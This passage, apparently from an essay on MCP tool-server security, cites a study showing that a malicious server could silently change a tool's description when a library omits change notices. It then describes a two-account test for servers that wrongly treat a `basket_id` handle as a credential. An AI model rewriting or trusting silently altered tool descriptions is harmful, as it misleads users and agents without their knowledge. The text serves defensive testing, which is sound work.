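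*Compatibility at a Cost* (March 2026) offers better support for Kale's concern. The study examined what happens when MCP libraries omit optional rules. The Python library omitted the rule on notices of changed tool lists, so a malicious server could change a tool's description without the user knowing. Some developers will probably omit the ownership check because it is optional too.

A company can use two accounts to test whether its own servers treat a handle, such as a `basket_id`, as a credential. It creates a basket as Alice, then calls `add_item` with her `basket_id` and Bob's token. If the item appears in Alice's basket, the server fails the test.
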